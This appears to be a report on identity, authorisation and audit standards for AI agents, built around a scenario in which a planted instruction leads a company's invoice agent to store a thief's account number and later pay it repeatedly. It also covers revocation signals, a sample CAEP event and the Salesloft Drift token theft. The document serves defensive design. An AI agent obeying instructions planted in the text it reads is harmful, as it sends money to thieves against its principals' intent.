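Suppose the thief is patient. A planted instruction leads the invoice agent to copy a false account number into Brandt Tools' record. Eight days later, the agent starts to pay €5,000 into that account every 10 seconds. Acme's database doesn't store where the number came from, so the payments pass every rule that Acme applies before paying. After two payments, a monitor detects that a supplier that normally gets one payment a month has received two in 10 seconds. Acme now has to withdraw the agent's authority to pay.

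### From an alarm to a refused payment

1. The monitor sends a warning to the payment service, the authorisation server and a program that manages SPIRE's registration entries.
2. The payment service discards the agent's access token and refuses further payments.
3. The authorisation server stops issuing tokens to the agent, and cancels its refresh token if it has one.
4. The program removes the agent's registration entry, so SPIRE doesn't renew the credential. The certificate that the agent already holds remains valid until it expires.

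Kasselman and colleagues suggest using the Shared Signals Framework for the warning. *OpenID Shared Signals Framework Specification 1.0* (Tulshibagwale, Cappalli and colleagues, 2025) defines how a transmitter, here the monitor, sends signed security events to receivers. Each receiver sets up a stream and specifies which types of event it should carry. The receiver can also specify which people or programs the events should cover. The transmitter either pushes events to the receiver or holds them until the receiver requests them.

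Two profiles define the events. Cappalli and Tulshibagwale (2025), in *OpenID Continuous Access Evaluation Profile 1.0* (CAEP), cover changes that affect access already in use, such as a revoked session, a changed credential or a new risk level. The other profile, RISC, covers the security of accounts. Scurtescu, Backman and colleagues (2025), in *OpenID RISC Profile Specification 1.0*, include an event for an account whose credentials need changing. RISC would be useful if someone stole Alice's password, while CAEP fits the hijacked agent better. The monitor could send this CAEP event, with the event type shortened here:

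```json
{
  "iss": "https://monitor.acme.example",
  "jti": "event-3107",
  "iat": 1796635272,
  "aud": "https://pay.acme.example",
  "txn": "alarm-3107",
  "sub_id": {
    "format": "uri",
    "uri": "spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice"
  },
  "events": {
    ".../caep/event-type/risk-level-change": {
      "event_timestamp": 1796635271,
      "principal": "WORKLOAD",
      "previous_level": "LOW",
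      "current_level": "HIGH",
      "risk_reason": "REPEATED_PAYMENTS_TO_ONE_SUPPLIER"
    }
  }
}
```

The framework allows events about "robotic principals", so an agent can be the subject of an event. CAEP lists users, devices and sessions among the values for `principal`, but not agents. It also permits other entities, so Acme chose "WORKLOAD" and has to make sure its receivers recognise that value.

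The choice of subject also determines who gets locked out. All copies of the invoice agent share one name, so this event could also stop Bob's copy. Acme could instead send a session-revoked event that names both Alice and the agent, which applies only to sessions that match both. If Acme adds its own field to identify the running copy, a receiver that doesn't support the field may ignore it and end too many sessions. Acme can mark the field as critical, but a receiver that can't process it must discard the whole event, so payments to the thief continue.

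A receiver doesn't have to obey these messages. The IETF standard describes them as statements of fact, "not commands issued between parties", and the Shared Signals Framework lets each deployment decide whether an event is only information or requires action. Kasselman and colleagues are stricter, requiring recipients to enforce a revocation without undue delay and to stop using cached tokens and decisions that are no longer valid.

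Events can also get lost. A transmitter may drop some of the events it holds while a stream is paused, and it may pause or delete a stream if the receiver is inactive for a period. Even a working stream may go weeks without an alarm, so a lack of alarms doesn't show whether the stream works. Receivers can request a test event, and Acme should do so regularly.

The OpenID Foundation (2025) announced the framework and both profiles as final specifications in September 2025. A separate interoperability profile, which would help products from different vendors use CAEP in the same way, isn't final. According to the OpenID Foundation's *Public Review Period for Proposed OpenID CAEP Interoperability Profile Final Specification* (2026), the working group decided in September 2026 to revise it and restart the review. Acme should therefore test each pair of products together before relying on them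 to stop a payment.

### What a hijacked agent can still spend

How much the agent can pay out after the alarm depends on which of its documents Acme stops.

| What Acme does | Time the agent can still pay | Payments | Worst-case loss |
|---|---|---|---|
| only stops renewing the workload credential | 60 + 5 minutes | 390 | €1.95 million |
| stops issuing access tokens | 5 minutes | 30 | €150,000 |
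| sends a signal that the payment service acts on within 20 seconds | 20 seconds | 2 | €10,000 |

In the worst case for the first row, SPIRE renewed the agent's credential just before the alarm. The agent can use that credential to get new access tokens for 60 minutes, and a token it gets in the last second works for another five minutes.

The figures rest on several assumptions:

- The clock starts at the alarm, so the two payments that caused it are extra.
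- Every payment is for the full €5,000, and the agent keeps to one every 10 seconds.
- The payment service accepts an access token until it expires, even if the agent's certificate has expired in the meantime.
- No cap on the total stops the payments, the account doesn't run dry, and the bank can't recall the money.

If the payment service also refuses expired certificates and closes open connections when their certificates expire, the figures in the first row fall to 60 minutes, 360 payments and €1.8 million. A receiver that polls for events once a minute, rather than having them pushed, could let through about six payments instead of two.

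The alarm may also come late. Each minute before it adds six payments, or €30,000:

loss = €5,000 × (*d* + *w*) / 10

Here *d* is the time in seconds from the first bad payment to the alarm, and *w* is the time in seconds from the alarm until the withdrawal takes effect. If the monitor takes 10 minutes to raise the alarm, Acme loses €310,000 with the signal and €450,000 if it only stops new tokens, a difference of €140,000. Detecting the fraud in five minutes instead of 10 would save €150,000. Acme should therefore spend at least as much effort on the monitor as on the speed of the signal.

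### Short lifetimes as a substitute for revocation

Kasselman and colleagues describe short-lived credentials as an alternative to explicit revocation. Whether that works depends on what went wrong. If a thief steals one access token, the token stops working within five minutes, even if nobody notices the theft. No revocation system can do that, because someone has to discover the theft first.

Expiry doesn't stop a hijacked agent. The agent still has its key and passes the same checks, so it gets a new token every five minutes and a new credential every half hour. Somebody has to tell the issuer to refuse these renewals, and that decision is a revocation, even if it takes effect only when the current token expires.

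Acme could shorten the delay by issuing 20-second tokens. The agent would then need 180 tokens an hour instead of 12, and an outage of the authorisation server would stop all payments within 20 seconds. A better option for payments may be token introspection, in which the payment service checks with the authorisation server whether a token is still active. For the invoice agent, that means 360 queries an hour, which is a light load. As long as the payment service doesn't cache the results, it will reject the first payment after the revocation. Like very short tokens, introspection depends on the authorisation server being available.

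### The Salesloft Drift theft

In August 2025, thieves used stolen OAuth tokens to copy data from the Salesforce accounts of companies that used Drift, Salesloft's AI chatbot. The tokens worked for whoever held them, so the thieves didn't need to deceive the chatbot. *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025) gives Google's account of the campaign. Infosecurity Magazine's *Salesloft* traces how the thieves obtained the tokens, and Cloudflare, one of the victims, published its own timeline.

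| Date in 2025 | Event |
|---|---|
| March to June | intruders use Salesloft's GitHub account; they later take customers' tokens from Drift's cloud environment |
| 8 August | earliest known theft of Salesforce data |
| 9 August | the thieves read email in a few Google Workspace accounts |
| 18 August | last known theft of Salesforce data |
| 20 August | Salesloft and Salesforce revoke Drift's access and refresh tokens |
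| 23 August | Salesforce and Salesloft notify Cloudflare |
| 28 August | Google reports that the thieves also had tokens for Drift's email connection |

Google told Cybersecurity Dive that it knew of more than 700 potentially affected organisations. Krebs on Security (2025) reports that the thieves also took tokens for hundreds of other online services that customers could connect to Salesloft, including Slack, Microsoft Azure and OpenAI.

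The theft from Cloudflare is evidence against relying on short token lifetimes alone. Salesforce Ben reports that the thieves copied the text of the company's support cases in just over three minutes, so even a five-minute token would have given them enough time. Short lifetimes could have made it harder for them to return on other days, but only if they had no refresh tokens for getting new access tokens.

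Revocation came 12 days after the first known theft and two days after the last. It was also incomplete, because Google had to revoke the tokens for Drift's email connection separately. In its notice of 20 August, Salesloft asked customers to reconnect Drift to Salesforce but, according to Krebs on Security, didn't mention that anyone had stolen tokens. A customer who read the notice had little reason to check the other services connected to Drift.

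A shared signal could have reached Cloudflare within seconds of the revocation instead of three days later, if the companies had already set up a stream between them. It couldn't have helped during the 12 days before the revocation. Joshua Wright, a security specialist quoted by Krebs on Security, explains that such attacks often go unnoticed because the attacker uses only access the victim has already granted.

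### What an audit record proves

Kasselman and colleagues require every deployment to keep durable logs that reveal tampering. They list the minimum contents, which could look like this for one of the agent's payments to the thief:

| Required field | Entry |
|---|---|
| authenticated agent identifier | `spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice` |
| user or system it acts for, if any | `alice@acme.example` |
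| resource or tool | payment service |
| action requested and decision | pay €5,000 to account ending 7719: permit |
| time and transaction number | 09:21:10, `txn-90466` |
| attestation results or risk level that influenced the decision | approved software, low risk |
| later remediation or revocation, and its cause | tokens revoked at 09:21:31, repeated payments |

If the log is accurate, it is good evidence of who acted. The caller proved that it held the invoice agent's key, Acme's server had issued a token for Alice, and the payment service permitted the request. Nobody could plausibly accuse Alice of entering the payment herself, and Checkwell's agent wasn't involved.

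But the record doesn't show that Alice wanted the payment. Her name is there because she approved the agent's access, perhaps days earlier. The record also doesn't show why the agent chose this account. The record of a genuine payment to Brandt Tools would differ only in the account number, amount, time and transaction number. None of the required fields covers the task, the text the agent had read or the model it used.

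Acme could record all three. An investigator could then rerun the model on the saved text with and without the suspicious line, many times each because the model's output can vary. If the model chooses the thief's account in most runs with the line and in none without it, the line probably caused the choice. This comparison is stronger evidence than the model's own explanation, but it requires access to the same version of the model.

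Rerunning the payment wouldn't be enough to investigate this theft, because the agent read the planted line eight days earlier. On the day of the payment, its context contained only a normal-looking supplier record. The investigator has to find out who last changed that record and then examine the task that made the change. Acme's log can support this only if it also records changes to supplier records, each with the transaction number of the task that made it.

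The draft doesn't prescribe a way to make tampering evident. A common one is to include in each entry a fingerprint of everything before it:

*h*ₙ = H(*h*ₙ₋₁, record *n*)

H is a hash function. If someone edits entry 5, its fingerprint changes, and so does every later one. An attacker who controls the whole log could recalculate them all, so Acme should regularly send the latest fingerprint to someone outside its own systems. Even then, the method can't reveal an event that nobody logged.

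Keeping logs out of an intruder's reach is just as important. The Drift thieves deleted the jobs they had used to extract data, but Larsen and colleagues found that this didn't affect the logs, so customers could still look for signs of the theft.

### Signed records and the AUDIT session

An ordinary log is weak evidence in a dispute because its owner could have written anything in it. If Brandt Tools never received its money, it would have to trust Acme's version of events. Several individual Internet-Drafts from 2026 propose records that others can check.

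*Signed Authorization-Evidence Records for WIMSE-Authorized AI Agent Actions* concerns whether an action had permission, and *Execution Context Tokens for Distributed Agentic Workflows* concerns work spread over several agents. Both were on the IETF's June list, but the WIMSE group had not adopted either.

In another draft at the IETF, the user signs a delegation receipt, which goes into an append-only log before the agent starts. Acme's server could then no longer forge Alice's approval, because only her private key can sign one. The receipt would help in a dispute between Alice and Acme, but it wouldn't explain the payment to the thief, because it is signed before the agent reads anything. *The Governance Audit Record (GAR) for Agentic AI Systems* (Sato, 2026) is aimed more at regulators and defines a package of records for outside inspection.

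As with transaction tokens, signing a record doesn't make its contents true. The proposals also overlap, and a company that adopts one can't expect its partners to be able to read its records. In *Agent Use of Delegation and Interaction Traceability (AUDIT)*, Kühlewind (2026) asked the IETF in May to consider a working group. Kühlewind argues that existing logs and authorisation systems each capture part of what happened but offer no common way to connect a user's intent, the chain of delegation, the permissions and the resulting actions across organisations. The group would define a common format for audit records and ways to pass audit information along with requests, building on OAuth, HTTP and the IETF's attestation work.

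The accompanying *Agent Auditing Architecture* (Kuehlewind and Birkholz, 2026) treats authorisation as a state that changes over time. An auditor could establish that the invoice agent had permission at 09:21:10 and had lost it by 09:21:31, and compare that with the bank's records. The design reuses attestation to provide evidence about the system that produced a record. It also uses SCITT, an IETF design for transparency services, to make it hard to deny later that the record existed.

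The IETF declined that first request on 6 July. The subject came up again at IETF 127 in November in a "birds of a feather" session, an open meeting to gauge whether there is enough interest and agreement to form a working group. The IETF's agenda included the difference between logging and auditing, privacy, and a draft charter. Speakers presented three use cases: end users, companies that set up cloud services, and the auditing of audio and text. The rules excluded presentations of solution drafts, and half an hour was set aside to discuss the scope. Flanagan confirms that the session took place, but it is still unclear whether a working group will follow.

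### The privacy cost of linkable records

The identifiers that let an auditor trace a payment from Alice to the bank also let others track Alice. Flanagan points out that an agent's records can reveal more than a browsing history because they may include what a person was trying to achieve and under what conditions. For example, a browsing history might show only that someone visited several airline websites, while an agent's records might show that they asked for a cheap flight that suits a medical condition and gets them to a job interview without their employer knowing.

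Kasselman and colleagues call for stable identifiers that let auditors establish which entity did what, but they also require companies to keep a user's identity from unrelated services. They recommend logging a token's number or hash instead of the whole token, which also keeps a thief from reusing tokens found in the log. Tulshibagwale and colleagues caution that warnings about security events may also contain personal information, and that even an error message can reveal whether someone has an account at a service.

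Acme can avoid much of the conflict by linking records by task instead of by person. It could give Checkwell and the bank a random transaction number for each payment and keep the list that connects those numbers to Alice. If a payment goes wrong, the three companies can match their records by that number. Unless there is a dispute, Checkwell can't tell whether two requests came from the same employee. Acme can still reconstruct everything Alice asked the agent to do, so it also needs rules on who may search the list and when to delete it.

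The saved text is more sensitive still. It is what an investigator most needs to find out why the agent paid the thief, but it may also contain private messages, suppliers' bank details and passwords that someone pasted into an email. The Drift thieves searched the stolen Salesforce data for such secrets. Decipher's *Cloudflare Details Salesloft Drift Breach* (2025) reports that Cloudflare searched the same data and found 104 of its own API tokens. Cloudflare saw no suspicious use of them but replaced them all. Acme should therefore remove credentials from the text before saving it, store it apart from the ordinary audit log, and delete it sooner than the log. But a week would be too soon, because in the Brandt Tools case the planted line would have been deleted a day before the first false payment.

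## Which standards bodies could extend identity frameworks to agents

Acme has had to invent several details, including the `account_source` field it sends to the decision point and the "WORKLOAD" value in its security events. Other companies' software won't recognise either. A standards body could define them for everyone, but the bodies have different remits, and much of their work on agents is at an early stage.

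| Body | Work on agents | Standing | Does it reach behaviour? |
|---|---|---|---|
| IETF, WIMSE group | AIMS | adopted draft | general requirements for monitoring and records |
| IETF, OAuth group | tokens, delegation, approval of tasks | drafts at different stages | through proposals to record the task |
| IETF, agentproto | communication between agents | proposed group, with a disputed charter | mostly excluded |
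| OpenID Foundation | AuthZEN, Shared Signals, AI identity community group | the two specifications are final; the group writes papers | yes, formats for decisions and warnings |
| NIST | demonstration project for companies' agents | planned | partly, by tracking where data came from |
| Linux Foundation | SPIFFE, MCP, A2A | in use | very little |
| Coalition for Secure AI | guidance on agents' access | version 1.0 | yes, as advice |

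### The IETF

The IETF writes the protocols that computers use to communicate over the internet. It doesn't certify products, so Acme has to test for itself whether a vendor's software follows a draft.

The WIMSE group now controls AIMS. The IETF's record for the individual draft by Kasselman and colleagues, last updated on 9 September 2026, lists `draft-ietf-wimse-aims` as its replacement. The IETF's *WIMSE Interim June 03 2026* (2026) records that everyone who gave an opinion on the work itself supported it. But Charles Eckel, the area director who oversees the group, couldn't clearly find it among the tasks in WIMSE's charter and suggested adjusting the text. Kasselman replied that the charter allows for best-practice documents and that the draft defines no new protocol. The chairs weren't ready to call for adoption at that point, because the group had to finish older documents first.

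Adoption settled where the work will happen, but not what builders can expect from the result. Acme can learn from a best-practice document which standards to combine, but two products that follow it may use different options and fail to work together. Paul Carleton, who spoke at the meeting from the MCP side, asked for specific example deployments, which would help a buyer more than another list of standards.

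The OAuth group has more existing deployments to keep working. *OAuth Is Asking What Authorization Needs to Become* (Flanagan, 2026) describes online meetings in September, with more planned for October, about whether some of OAuth's old assumptions still hold. The 14 September meeting was about how to tie an access token to a key. OAuth already has a method for this, DPoP, but the new proposal uses HTTP Message Signatures instead. That could suit Acme, whose agent may already sign its payment requests this way for WIMSE. Flanagan cautions, however, that the group can discuss a proposal without accepting it as a standard.

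In November the OAuth and WIMSE groups held a joint session on what an agent's identifier should identify. Flanagan suspects that deciding when to use the new mechanisms and what information to send through them will be at least as hard as developing them. For example, a service called by a sub-agent may need to know the sub-agent's permissions but not which agent started it or on whose behalf.

Some engineers want a separate group for communication between agents. The IETF held a two-hour session in Vienna on 23 July to decide whether to form one, under the working name "agentproto". According to draft minutes from the IETF (2026), the shows of hands went as follows:

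| Question | Yes | No | No opinion |
|---|---|---|---|
| Is the problem well understood, solvable and useful to solve? | 124 | 72 | 14 |
| Is the IETF the right place? | 158 | 30 | 14 |
| Is the initial scope correct? | 38 | 124 | 40 |
| Are the initial deliverables correct? | 92 | 58 | 49 |
| Should the IETF form a working group? | 154 | 51 | 5 |
| Will you help write or review drafts? | 137 | 17 | 40 |
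| Will you implement the protocols? | 42 | 28 | 40 |

People could support forming a group while rejecting the proposed scope, because the question about forming a group referred to a charter "based on" the draft. That wording appears in the IETF's slides, *Agent Communication Protocols (agentproto)* (2026). The minutes shorten the question to "Form a WG with this charter?", which makes the two votes look more contradictory than they were. None of the votes is binding. The last row matters most to a company choosing what to build on, because far fewer people offered to implement the protocols than to write about them.

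The draft charter excludes agents' behaviour, decision-making and planning. It also excludes "behavioral security", though a protocol could still include a request for a user to confirm an action. The proponents weren't consistent about this, since on another slide they promised "behavior-driven scopes" with "dynamic behavioral boundaries". Altanai Bisht objected to the exclusion and wanted the protocol to provide signals that help applications detect misuse. Suresh Krishnan of Cisco, one of the proponents, expected the OAuth group to handle what an agent may do and how to communicate policy.

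This leaves no IETF group clearly responsible for agent behaviour. The proposed group refers the question to OAuth, and AIMS leaves the policy format to each company. OAuth proposals such as McGuinness's missions record a task, but Acme can't yet treat any of them as settled.

After the July session, Eckel confirmed that there would be a new mailing list, where the chairs planned to revise the scope. In an account of the November meeting, Flanagan lists OAuth, WIMSE and AUDIT (the session on audit records) as the places where identity specialists were busy, and doesn't mention agentproto. Acme shouldn't plan around an agentproto standard until the IETF has at least approved a charter.

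Web Bot Auth, a smaller IETF group, could matter sooner if the invoice agent has to collect invoices from suppliers' websites. The group is working on a way for automated visitors to prove to a website who they are (Flanagan, 2026, *W3C, IETF, and the Emerging Shape of AI Standards*). A supplier could then admit Acme's agent and block unknown bots, but it would still have to decide which pages the agent may open.

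### The OpenID Foundation

The OpenID Foundation has already finished two standards that help with decisions about behaviour. AuthZEN lets systems check whether an action is allowed, and the Shared Signals Framework lets them send warnings to each other. Acme can buy products that support these standards without waiting for agent-specific work.

The Foundation also has a community group on AI identity, whose members come from technology companies, banks, security vendors and independent research. In its response to NIST, the OpenID Foundation (2026) describes a subgroup that catalogues threats, concentrating on cases where users and agents expect finer control than identity systems provide. The community group's first major publication was South's white paper of October 2025.

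A community group's papers can identify gaps, but the Foundation's working groups write the specifications. Flanagan (2026), in *Do We Need New Protocols, or Better Architecture?*, reports that Dick Hardt's AAuth proposal, a newer protocol for agents, has become an input to work at the Foundation. Any specification that results may look quite different from the proposal.

### NIST

NIST's cybersecurity centre, the NCCoE, builds example systems from commercial products and publishes guides to them. It doesn't plan to write a new agent protocol, but a guide could still influence what companies buy because it shows a working combination of products.

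The concept paper by Booth and colleagues was open for comment from 5 February to 2 April 2026. Galluzzo (2026), in *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*, reports more than 600 formal responses, and in November still described the demonstration project as planned. The standards under consideration include OAuth, MCP and SPIFFE. They also include two that could fill practical gaps at Acme:

- **SCIM** automates the creation, updating and removal of accounts across systems. Acme could use it to remove a retired agent everywhere, so that nobody has to remember each service.
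- **Next Generation Access Control** represents users, data and rules as one connected graph. An event can change the rules, for example when an agent gains access to a new tool.

The concept paper comes closer to behavioural authorisation than most identity work. One of its five areas of interest is tracking the sources of user prompts and other input to support decisions about what an agent does. Acme would need this information to enforce its rule against using account numbers from emails. The paper also includes questions about how an agent might convey the intent of its actions and how to limit the damage after a successful prompt injection.

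The project will start with agents inside companies, because they are easier to control and observe. It won't initially cover external agents from untrusted sources. A guide might therefore help Acme with its invoice agent, but be less useful when first dealing with an unknown supplier's agent.

NIST has continued to cover the subject in a series of blog posts. The first, on identity foundations, appeared in August and described the shared logins and static keys discussed earlier. *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems*, by Booth and three colleagues (2026), followed on 27 October. These posts usefully suggest the agency's direction, but a company can't certify a product against them.

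Another NIST project, COSAiS, may reach auditors sooner than builders. According to the consultancy IDMWORKS, it adapts SP 800-53, NIST's catalogue of security controls, to AI systems. Two of its five use cases concern single agents and groups of agents. If Acme's auditors adopt the result, they could ask whether the company has a particular control, regardless of which protocol provides it.

### The Linux Foundation and other bodies

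The Linux Foundation hosts open-source projects, so its standards usually develop alongside working code. One of them is SPIFFE, which belongs to the Cloud Native Computing Foundation, a part of the Linux Foundation. SPIFFE is the most established option here for naming workloads and issuing credentials. It covers only identity, and extending it to authorize payments would require giving it information it doesn't otherwise need.

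MCP, also at the Linux Foundation, connects agents to tools. Agent2Agent (A2A), which Google introduced in 2025, lets one agent hand a task to another. An agent using A2A publishes an "agent card", a file that describes what the agent can do, where to reach it and how to authenticate. Acme's invoice agent could read Checkwell's card, obtain a token and send the account check as a task.

MCP and A2A offer different help to anyone checking an agent's history. Enforcing a rule such as "no more than one payment per bill in this task" requires knowing which calls belong to the same task. In the July minutes, Maxwell Gerber points out that the coming version of MCP removes sessions. Acme therefore can't use an MCP session number to group the calls and has to send its own task number. Parisa Foroughi notes that A2A already has identifiers for tasks and results, and a context identifier that agents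 share when they work towards the same objective.

These identifiers don't prove anything by themselves. Checkwell's agent could attach the right task number to a false "account confirmed", and Acme would know only which task the answer belonged to. But the identifiers are a good basis for totals and records. Brian Trammell suggested at the July session that the IETF could define what a context identifier means and let A2A use the definition.

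The Coalition for Secure AI covers more of agents' behaviour than any of these protocols do. Its March 2026 guidance addresses decision points, policy languages and checks at each tool. Acme can use it as a design checklist today, but following the same guidance doesn't ensure that two vendors' software will exchange messages correctly.

The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) sets standards for websites and browsers. It also has a standard for verifiable credentials, which are signed statements that a holder can show to different organisations. These could record an agent's certification or an employee's authority. Some of W3C's newer work on agents takes place in community groups, whose reports aren't W3C standards. This work is worth following if agents will act through browsers, but Acme doesn't need it to connect its agent to an internal payment service.

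Flanagan also lists ISO and the ITU's standards arm, ITU-T, among the organisations working on AI. ISO's management standard for AI, ISO/IEC 42001, covers how an organisation assigns responsibility and manages risk. It can support an audit of Acme, but it doesn't define any messages for the invoice agent to send. At the July session, Arnaud Taddei urged the IETF to use existing ITU work rather than redefine identity and its terms. Acme doesn't need to delay the invoice agent to wait for either body.

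### Three strategies for agents

The standards bodies' choices depend partly on a dispute over how much about agent identity is new. Supporters of AIMS want to combine existing standards, while others want to extend OAuth or design a new protocol. Two independent proposals from the second group are both called AAuth, so it is safer to identify them by author.

AIMS combines existing standards to give agents identities. Lombardo, who co-wrote it, argues in *Assembly Required* that "we don't have a standards gap. We have an assembly gap." Lombardo had seen new proposals for agents reinvent token formats and even the concept of workload identity, so the AIMS team decided to use whatever already works and to name a gap only where something is missing.

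As evidence that this works, Lombardo points to OpenAI, Anthropic and Snowflake, which now let workloads connect to their platforms without static API keys. That is good evidence for the identity part, but much weaker evidence that the same combination can handle an approval halfway through a payment.

The gaps have also produced new drafts, so combining standards still involves writing some. One of them, *OAuth Transaction Authorization Challenge*, addresses the problem that only the client can start CIBA, the protocol that sends an approval request to Alice's phone. For the payment to Brandt Tools, the new method could work like this:

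1. The agent asks the payment service to send €4,800 to an unfamiliar account.
2. The service refuses for now and returns a signed challenge that describes the approval it needs.
3. The agent passes the challenge to a client, which presents it to the authorisation server.
4. The server obtains Alice's approval and issues an access token for this transaction only.
5. The agent repeats its request with the new token.

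The payment service now determines what Alice has to approve, instead of the agent. The service signs the challenge, so a deceived agent can't change the account number in it without breaking the signature. Alice still has to notice that the account is wrong. Four engineers wrote the draft, and three of them also helped write AIMS.

The early version of Jonathan Rosenberg and Pat White's AAuth extends OAuth with a new grant for users who reach an agent by phone or text message. OAuth handles this case badly because the agent can't send the user to a login page in a browser. Under the new grant, the agent asks the user for identifying details in conversation, and the authorisation server checks them before issuing an access token with limited permissions. Downstream services can then accept the token much as they accept any other.

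The main attraction is that the payment service changes little. The weak point is the conversation, because a thief who knows Alice's date of birth and address might answer the questions correctly, and a language model might supply a detail that the caller never gave. Rosenberg and White treat impersonation through such invented details as a central risk. Acme could reasonably let Alice use a method like this to ask whether an invoice has been paid, but should require a stronger login before a payment.

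Hardt, who edited the OAuth 2.0 standard, thinks agents need a different starting point and has proposed a new protocol called AAuth. In its early design, an agent signs its requests with its own key, so it doesn't have to register as a client with every service beforehand. This suits agents that discover new services while they work. In July, Hardt also objected to the term "session" because it suggests a connection between two parties, whereas a "mission" gives context to many interactions in pursuit of one goal.

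Ted Hardie replied that a token showing that a request belongs to mission X should stay separate from a token that authorises the request. Otherwise, a payment service could mistake "this is part of Alice's invoice task" for "Alice permits this payment". Jeff Lombardo similarly described a mission as the state of the original request and the work that follows from it, not as the technical connection between the parties.

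A new protocol could avoid awkward features that OAuth keeps for older software, but Acme, its software vendors and its suppliers would all have to adopt it. During the transition, Acme would also have to keep its OAuth system running and prevent agents from using the weaker of the two protocols.

### One payment under each strategy

Suppose Alice phones the invoice agent from a train and asks it to pay this week's invoices. One is the forged invoice from Brandt Tools with the new account number. The three strategies would handle her request differently:

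| | Combine (AIMS) | Extend OAuth (Rosenberg and White) | New protocol (Hardt) |
|---|---|---|---|
| How Alice gives authority | she logs in through a browser or approves on her phone | she answers identifying questions during the call | she approves a mission |
| What the agent presents | its workload credential and an access token | an OAuth access token | signed requests and proof of its authority |
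| What has to change | Acme connects standards it may already use | the authorisation server supports a new grant | the agent, the services and their servers support a new protocol |
| What could stop the forged payment | a rule at the payment service, or an approval challenge | a rule at the payment service | a comparison with the mission, if it lists permitted accounts |

None of these proposals detects the forgery by default. Rosenberg and White's proposal helps Alice authorise work without a browser, but it doesn't show the payment service that the account number is false. Hardt's mission may give the service more information to check the payment against, but only if someone has stated the task precisely. Under AIMS, a challenge gives Alice a chance to stop the payment, but only if the service issues it when it's needed.

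For Acme, combining existing standards is the best starting point because most of its systems already use OAuth and it can replace one component without changing the rest. It should still test extensions for particular needs, such as approval during a task. A new protocol would have to offer a large benefit across many services to justify running two systems.

However, companies may adopt a method before it becomes a formal standard. The Workload Authorization Grant by Carleton and colleagues is still an individual draft, but Pogorelec reports that Datadog and PostHog accept its grants in their MCP servers. If a supplier insists on an early method, Acme can support it where its systems connect to the supplier's and keep its own services on standards that change less often.

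### What could become a common standard

At the July session, Mark Nottingham asked why a protocol should include context when the programs at each end could manage it. Inside one company, there may be no good reason, since Acme can give its agent program and payment service any field names it likes. It needs a standard when information crosses between vendors or organisations that would otherwise have to agree on the format each time.

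| Part of the decision | What a standard could define | What Acme still has to decide |
|---|---|---|
| Question and answer | names for the task, the source of data and earlier actions | which combinations to refuse |
| Task | its number, approver, expiry and current state | what counts as "this week's invoices" |
| Source of data | labels such as "email" and rules for passing them on | which sources to trust for an account number |
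| Warning | events for a suspended or hijacked agent | how much evidence justifies a suspension |
| Approval | a challenge and a signed answer | who must approve, and above what amount |
| Record | common fields and a way to match transactions | who may read the records, and for how long |

Warnings and approvals seem closest to having a useful common format, because both build on existing methods. *Workload Identity Security Events* (WISE), one of the drafts Lombardo describes, extends Shared Signals to workloads, including events for replaced credentials, withdrawn trust and changes in a workload's security state. With a finished version, Acme might not have to explain its "WORKLOAD" value to every vendor. The receiver would still have to work out whether two payments in 10 seconds are fraud or just unusually heavy activity.

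Decision requests are also good candidates for standardisation. AuthZEN already defines their outer format, and a further profile could name the fields for task, source and history. Omissions would then be easier to notice, because a buyer could ask whether a product supports the `account_source` field or its agreed equivalent, a more specific question than whether it has "behavioural controls".

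Naveed Ihsanullah pointed out in July that sessions end and credentials expire, while investigators need a lasting record of who was responsible for an agent. A standard could define an owner field, but Acme would have to update it when the responsible employee changes jobs. Otherwise an auditor would find a valid record that names someone who left two years ago.

Information about the task and its data will be harder to share. Stephen Farrell warned at the session that authorisation information for agents is very complicated and that nobody had yet shown how to share it safely. Justin Richer added that not every part of a system should know everything. If Acme sent Checkwell Alice's full instructions and every source label, this might help Checkwell judge one request but also reveal Acme's other suppliers.

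As a compromise, Artur Hecker proposed keeping the contents separate from the protocol and standardising little more than descriptive information and pointers to closed blocks of data. Acme could send Checkwell a task number, an expiry time and a reference to return with its answer, while the full list of invoices would stay at Acme. Acme could then match the answer to the task, but Checkwell couldn't independently decide whether the task made sense.

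Standards could plausibly be more detailed for one kind of action, such as paying invoices, than for agents in general, since a hospital's agent would need different terms and tests. Banks and accounting companies could agree on what "new account", "approved supplier" and "duplicate payment" mean, because they need the same facts for most invoices. They could then write test cases, such as three payments on one bill, and check that different products classify them correctly.

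Even then, each company will probably still make the final judgement itself. Acme may accept a new account after one phone call, while another company requires two employees to approve it, but both can use the same request and record formats. A common standard is even less suited to deciding whether a payment fits the spirit of Alice's instruction.

Acme can protect its payments without waiting for these formats. It can keep its invented fields in one small translation layer, separate from the rules that use them. If AuthZEN or another group later defines an equivalent of `account_source`, Acme can update that layer without changing its rule against using account numbers from emails.
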